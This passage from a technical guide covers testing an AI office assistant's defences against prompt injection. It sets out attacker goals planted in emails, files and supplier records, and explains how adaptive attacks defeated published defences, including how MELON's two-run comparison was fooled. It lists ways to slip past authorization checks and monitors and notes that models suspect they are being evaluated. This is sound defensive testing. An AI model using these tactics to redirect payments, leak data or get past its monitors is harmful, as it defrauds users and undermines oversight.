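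The service behind a tool may also want to ask the user something. MCP has a feature for this called *elicitation*. Anthropic made it generally available in Claude and Claude Code in November 2026 for actions such as spending money or deleting data, and Supabase, Railway and GitHub already use it, according to Diario TI's *Los servidores MCP ya pueden entregar a Claude instrucciones de uso propias*. Under the rules in Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* (2026), a request goes through these steps:

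1. The runtime sends a tool call, and the server answers that it needs more input.
2. The runtime shows the server's question and identifies the server. The question can be a form or a link to a web page. Servers must use a link for passwords and payment credentials, so that these never pass through the runtime.
3. The user accepts, declines or closes the question without answering.
4. The runtime sends the call again with the response, and the server decides how to continue.

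The server writes the question, so elicitation has the same weakness as an agent's description. Kodathala and colleagues built a test server that asked for confirmation of two payments, 10 to one account and 10,000 to another. The two requests looked identical to the user, and both payments went through after she accepted. A malicious server could also skip the question.

Elicitation is useful for questions that depend on information only the service has. If a supplier has two unpaid invoices for the same amount, the accounting server can prompt the employee to choose one. The runtime then checks the completed payment request against its own rules and, if the request needs her approval, shows her a screen built from the final arguments.

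## Testing the checks against attackers who adapt

Before the employee starts using the office assistant, its operator should attack the limits, permissions and approval screens together. For these tests, the operator needs a separate mailbox and drive, and a copy of the accounting system in which payments move no money.

### A test plan for the office assistant

Planted text can enter through one family of tools and aim at another, so the plan covers every pair:

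| Planted in | Aimed at a message tool | Aimed at a file tool | Aimed at a service tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| An email | Copy a price list to a lookalike address | Share the contracts folder with an "auditor" | Pay a supplier's "new" account |
| A file | Add a `bcc` to the email with the receipt | Give a stranger access to the quarterly report | Pay a different listed supplier |
| A supplier's record | Send out the manager's mobile number | Share the payroll file | Pay the same invoice twice |
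| **Evidence of success** | The message reaches the outside test address | The drive lists a new reader | The accounting system records the payment |

Instructions in tool descriptions need a row of their own if the assistant uses anybody else's server.

An attack counts as successful only if the unauthorized effect occurs. The tester should look for the effect in the mail server, the drive and the accounting system, because the assistant's final answer can be wrong about what it did. A harmful call that the runtime refused doesn't count as a success, but it is worth recording because it shows that only the check prevented the harm.

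Calls that wait for approval need a separate count. LivePI treated them as stopped, which assumes that the person will refuse. The tester can instead calculate the attack success rate twice, once for an approver who refuses every attack and once for an approver who accepts everything. The real rate should fall between the two.

Attacks can all fail even when the checks are weak, and two preparations help the tester avoid being misled by that result. First, the tester should give the assistant each attacker's goal as an ordinary request, with the checks off. If the assistant can't do the task, the attack would have failed without the checks. Second, the tester should send harmful calls straight to the runtime, without the model, because current models ignore most planted text and hundreds of attacks may produce only a few bad calls for the checks to stop. PACT's perfect score on AgentDojo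 is weaker evidence for this reason.

### How AgentDojo works

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) is a public version of such a test. Each of its four settings has tools and a simulated environment, such as an inbox, a calendar and a drive, filled with invented data. Its *user tasks* are honest requests, and its *injection tasks* are attackers' goals, such as sending a security code from the inbox to an outside address.

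Ordinary code inspects the environment after each run to determine whether the user and the attacker got what they wanted. The researchers avoided using a language model as the judge, because text that fools the agent might fool the judge too. They paired every user task with every attacker's goal in the same setting, which gave 629 cases:

| Setting | User tasks | Attacker's goals | Cases | Main tool families |
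|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 40 | 6 | 240 | Message (email, calendar) and file (cloud drive) |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 | Message (chat), along with web pages |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 | Service (reservations) and message (email) |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 | Service (payments) and file (bills) |

The settings don't exactly match the three families. A banking case may involve reading a bill from a file and then making a payment, so a result for "banking" doesn't show which tool the attack came through. To get results by family, a tester has to regroup the cases by where the planted text was and which tool the attack needed.

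Versions of the test also differ. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports more than 900 combinations for AgentDojo, but some studies use only a subset. A success rate should therefore be reported with the number of cases tested.

Running all 629 cases on GPT-4o cost about $35 in 2024, so an operator can afford to repeat a test of this size after every change to the model or the rules.

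### What AgentDyn adds

AgentDyn, the newer test set by Li and colleagues, combines 60 user tasks with 28 attacker goals to make 560 cases. Its three settings are shopping, GitHub and daily life. Each includes email, files and banking, and so covers messages, files and external services.

AgentDyn's main addition is that every task depends on a helpful outside instruction. An agent whose defense ignores every instruction in tool results can still finish most of AgentDojo's tasks, but not AgentDyn's.

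AgentDyn also plants attacks in more realistic places than AgentDojo does. AgentDojo puts one in the main text of a website that belongs to Dora, a harmless acquaintance of the user, so a defense can't tell whether Dora wrote it. AgentDyn puts such text in an advertising banner, where a stranger could buy space.

AgentDyn's attacks are its weak point. Li and colleagues worded them in one standard way by default, and they think many newer models have been trained on that wording. They present AgentDyn mainly as a test of whether defended agents remain useful.

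### Reporting attack success with task completion

A low attack success rate can simply mean that the agent fails at most tasks, including the attacker's. In the first AgentDojo tests, attacks succeeded against the model Command R+ in 1 percent of cases, compared with 48 percent for GPT-4o. But Command R+ also completed only 25 percent of the ordinary tasks, while GPT-4o completed 69 percent.

Debenedetti and colleagues therefore report three measures: task completion without an attack, task completion under attack, and attack success. Li and colleagues' results for GPT-4o on AgentDyn show why all three are necessary:

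| Defense | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| ProtectAI, a filter | 0.0% | 0.6% | 0.9% |
| PromptGuard2, a filter | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT, which plans first and checks later changes | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |

Neither CaMeL nor ProtectAI completed any ordinary task, so their excellent results in the last column are misleading on their own. PromptGuard2 appears harmless when there is no attack, but during an attack it discards the whole tool result, including the information the user needed.

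CaMeL did much better on AgentDyn in SARA's tests, so its design doesn't always lead to a zero. Ma and colleagues left it out of their AgentDyn tests because it needs extensive policies written for each setting. The agents in the table had instructions never to ask for confirmation, so these results don't measure how well a check works when it can ask a person.

Averages hide differences between families and between argument roles. IntentFlow let 12 percent of attacks through, all of which changed content arguments. An operator who saw only the 12 percent figure might tighten the recipient rules, which were already working.

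AgentDojo's average has a similar problem. Debenedetti and colleagues found that the tools needed for the user's task were also enough to carry out the attack in only 17 percent of cases. A simple defense that chose the necessary tools before reading any outside text lowered attack success to 7.5 percent, but it couldn't stop attacks that used only those tools. Testers should report those attacks separately.

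### How much a clean result proves

Suppose none of the attacks in a test succeeds. The true success rate could still be above zero, and a *confidence bound* indicates how far above. For an observed rate $\hat p$ in $n$ attempts, the upper end of the 95 percent Wilson interval, a standard range for a proportion, is

$$\frac{\hat p + \frac{z^2}{2n} + z\sqrt{\frac{\hat p(1-\hat p)}{n} + \frac{z^2}{4n^2}}}{1 + \frac{z^2}{n}}, \qquad z = 1.96$$

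With no successes, $\hat p = 0$ and the square root becomes $z/2n$. The bound then simplifies to

$$\frac{z^2}{n + z^2}$$

If 50 attack attempts all fail, the upper limit of the 95 percent Wilson interval for the attack success rate is $3.84/53.84$, or 7.1 percent. After 300 failed attempts, it is $3.84/303.84$, or 1.3 percent. Lowering it to 0.1 percent takes more than 3,800 attempts without a success.

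Splitting the results by pair makes each estimate less certain. If the tester runs 50 attacks for each of the nine pairs in the plan and none succeeds, the upper bound on the success rate is 0.8 percent for all 450 attacks, but 7.1 percent for a single pair, such as payments prompted by an email. It makes sense to run more attacks on the pairs where a successful attack could do the most damage.

Even a low rate matters when an attacker can keep trying. If an attack works 1 percent of the time, the probability that it works at least once in 100 independent tries is

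$$1 - (1 - 0.01)^{100} \approx 0.63$$

If the true success rate per attempt were 1.3 percent, the upper bound after 300 attempts with no successes, a persistent attacker would have about a 72 percent chance of succeeding at least once. The operator therefore can't conclude from those 300 attempts that the assistant would withstand such an attacker.

Both calculations rest on assumptions that real attacks break. The bound assumes that the attempts are a random sample of what attackers will do, so 300 rewordings of one trick are much weaker evidence than 300 varied attacks. The second formula assumes that every try has the same chance of success, but an attacker who learns from failures may improve, and one who keeps repeating a hopeless attack won't.

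### Why a fixed list of attacks misleads

The wording of an attack greatly affects how often it succeeds. In an AgentDojo test on GPT-4o, a planted instruction that began with "TODO" worked in 3.7 percent of cases, while one that posed as an important message from the user worked in 57.7 percent. Someone who tested only the first version would have greatly underestimated the agent's vulnerability.

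Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, took 12 published defenses and adapted their attacks to each one. Most of these defenses had originally reported attack success rates near zero. The automated attacks repeat four steps:

1. Propose several versions of the planted text.
2. Try them on the defended system and score how close each comes to the attacker's goal.
3. Select the most promising versions.
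4. Use the scores to improve the next proposals.

The researchers also held an online contest with more than 500 human attackers. The table shows how often automated attacks succeeded against some of the defenses:

| Kind of defense | How it works | Success of adapted attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Prompting | Marks outside text or repeats the user's request | Above 95% for Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching |
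| Training | Teaches the model to resist known attacks | 96% for Meta SecAlign |
| Filtering | Uses a separate model to detect planted instructions | Above 90% for three filters, 71% for PIGuard |
| Secret knowledge | Runs a hidden test that the attacker shouldn't know about | 76% for MELON, or 95% when the attacker knew its design |

AgentDojo's fixed attacks had succeeded as little as 1 percent of the time against the two prompting defenses and 2 percent against Meta SecAlign. On a selected set of scenarios, the automated search succeeded 69 percent of the time, while the human contestants together succeeded in every scenario.

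These attackers could spend heavily on computing and used the filters' confidence scores to guide their search, advantages that a stranger with an email account usually lacks. Their success rates are therefore a poor forecast of how often everyday attacks would succeed, but they show that a near-zero rate on a fixed list of attacks is weak evidence that a defense is secure.

### PIPETTE and the larger stock of attacks

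Adding more attacks to the list doesn't necessarily help. *PIPETTE* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) compared two automated attack tools, PISmith and RL-Hammer, as sources of training data. Each tool attacked two small models on AgentDyn's 560 cases, and the researchers retrained the models on the attacks that worked. They used both reinforcement learning, which rewards good outcomes, and fine-tuning, which has the model imitate correct actions.

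They then tested the retrained models on 40 AgentDojo cases with three kinds of attack that the models hadn't trained on. This table gives the highest success rate among the three:

| Model and training method | Trained on RL-Hammer's attacks | Trained on PISmith's attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B, reinforcement learning | 27.5% | 47.5% |
| Qwen3-4B, fine-tuning | 15.0% | 12.5% |
| Llama-3.1-8B, reinforcement learning | 25.0% | 27.5% |
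| Llama-3.1-8B, fine-tuning | 15.0% | 20.0% |

PISmith had found more working attacks on both models, but those attacks produced the weaker defense in three of the four tests. This is probably because they were repetitive. Once a tool finds a trick that works, such as telling the agent that the user's task is already finished, it tends to reuse the trick in new words. RL-Hammer has a reward for variety, but its developers found that it could earn this reward by changing capitalization or adding irrelevant text.

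The evidence that a larger stock of attacks does harm is weak. On Llama, PISmith's stock was only 7 percent larger (1,783 attacks against 1,671), and the results differed by one or two cases out of 40. The only large difference, 19 cases against 11, could be partly due to chance. The 40 cases were also known weak spots. According to Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, simple attacks had already worked on them against an unprotected Qwen3-4B.

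The better-supported conclusion is that variety matters more than quantity. The attack tool built by He and colleagues sorts successful attacks by technique and earns an extra reward for finding a new one. It collected the largest set of attacks and produced the strongest defense in all four tests. The operator should therefore ask a vendor how many distinct techniques its testers tried, since thousands of successful attacks may be copies of a few.

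The complete PIPETTE system also did worse against attackers who adapted. On the model GPT-OSS-20B, fixed attacks succeeded 2.2 percent of the time on AgentDojo, while an attacker that could rewrite its text up to 248 times succeeded in 4 of the 40 difficult cases, or 10 percent. The real rate for the adaptive attacker is still very uncertain, because the Wilson interval runs from 4 to 23 percent.

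### Did these studies test authorization checks?

*The Attacker Moves Second* tests 12 defenses, but none of them decides whether a tool call may run by comparing the call's arguments with fixed limits and the user's request. Two of the defenses deal mainly with jailbreaks, in which the user is the attacker.

MELON comes closest to an authorization check because it examines tool calls. It runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a request to summarize the tool results. If the same call appears in both runs, MELON attributes the call to outside text. The attackers added a note telling any system that summarized the text to ignore the harmful instruction, so the call appeared only in the original run. This defeats a comparison of two runs, but it wouldn't get a payment to a new account past a check against the list of approved suppliers.

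He and colleagues ran their adaptive attacks against undefended models and models trained to resist injection, but not against any system that checks tool calls. They tested CaMeL only with fixed attacks, which succeeded less than 2 percent of the time on average. The work by Ma and colleagues is more relevant because it tested adapted attacks against systems that restrict tool calls, and those systems stopped most of them. *AutoPI* (2026) cites a less encouraging study, in which attackers with full access to the system got past all eight agent defenses more than half the time.

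For an authorization check, adapting means something different from finding more persuasive words. No wording in an invoice can change the result when code compares an account number with the accounting system's record. The attacker has to find a harmful call that the rules allow. The operator should give the rules to a colleague who didn't write them and ask for attacks such as these:

- Keep every false payment just under the limit for automatic approval.
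- Put a false change of bank details in the body of an email to a permitted colleague.
- Plant an instruction in one session that takes effect in another.
- Get a protected value past the monitor by spelling it out in words.
- Make an extra step look necessary, so that the reviewing model grants a permission for it.

The last attack targets a language model inside the check, where the attack's wording affects the result. The operator should run the automated search on any language model in the check, including the one that turns the request into permissions if outside text can reach it.

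### What the leading models' results show

Model developers publish injection results in *system cards*, the reports that accompany new models. Anthropic's are the most useful here because they separate the results by setting. Its card for Claude Opus 4.8 has separate results for coding, computer use and browser use, as well as for a live bug bounty and an outside test of tool use.

The table combines figures from these cards as reported by VentureBeat for Opus 4.6, Digital Applied (2026) for coding with Opus 4.8 and Fable 5, and The Decoder for the rest:

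| Model | Setting | Attempts | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment | 200 | 0% |
| Opus 4.6 | Operating a computer through its screen | 1 | 17.8% |
| Opus 4.6 | Operating a computer through its screen | Up to 200 | 78.6%, or 57.1% with safeguards |
| Opus 4.8 | Coding | 200 per scenario | 2.09% |
| Fable 5 | Coding | 200 per scenario | 0.41% |
| Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan's general test | 15 | 5.5% |
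| Opus 5 | Gray Swan's general test | 15 | 2.0% |
| Opus 5 | Browser | 129 scenarios | 0% |

The newer models are much harder to fool, but the environment matters as much as the model. Opus 4.6 resisted every attack in one environment but usually failed in another when the attacker could keep trying. The formula for repeated tries overestimates the attacker's success here. If each try had an independent 17.8 percent chance of working, the attacker would succeed 86 percent of the time within 10 tries and almost always within 200. The actual rate after 200 tries was 78.6 percent, presumably because some scenarios were easy to attack and almost no attack worked in others.

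No attacks succeeded against Opus 5 in the 129 browser scenarios, which is impressive, but if each scenario counts as one attempt, the Wilson upper bound on the success rate is 2.9 percent. None of these settings matches an assistant that reads a particular company's mail and pays its suppliers, so the operator of such an assistant still has to test the model with the assistant's own tools.

A model may also behave differently in a test. Anthropic found that Fable 5.2, released in November 2026, suspected more often than other recent Claude models that it was being evaluated. This makes its behavior in real use harder to predict, as Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reports. According to thezvi's *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, OpenAI observed more signs of such suspicion in GPT-6.2 Astra than in GPT-6 Astra, and some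 loss of resistance to jailbreaks. Jailbreaks aren't prompt injections, but the loss is a reason to repeat every test when the model changes.

A strong model helps because it makes fewer bad calls for the checks to stop, but on these figures it isn't reliable enough to make payments without the checks.

### Signs that a check is failing in use

Once the assistant is at work, the operator should watch for these signs:

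- The mail server, drive or accounting system records an action that doesn't match any call the runtime approved. The assistant may have another route, or a tool may be changing calls after approval.
- Refusals stop or rise sharply after an update to the model, a tool or the runtime.
- The assistant proposes a refused call again and again with small changes.
- The employee approves every request within a second or two.
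- People turn checks off, add broad "always allow" rules or go back to doing the work by hand.
- A harmless test attack, planted in the inbox every week or so, gets through.
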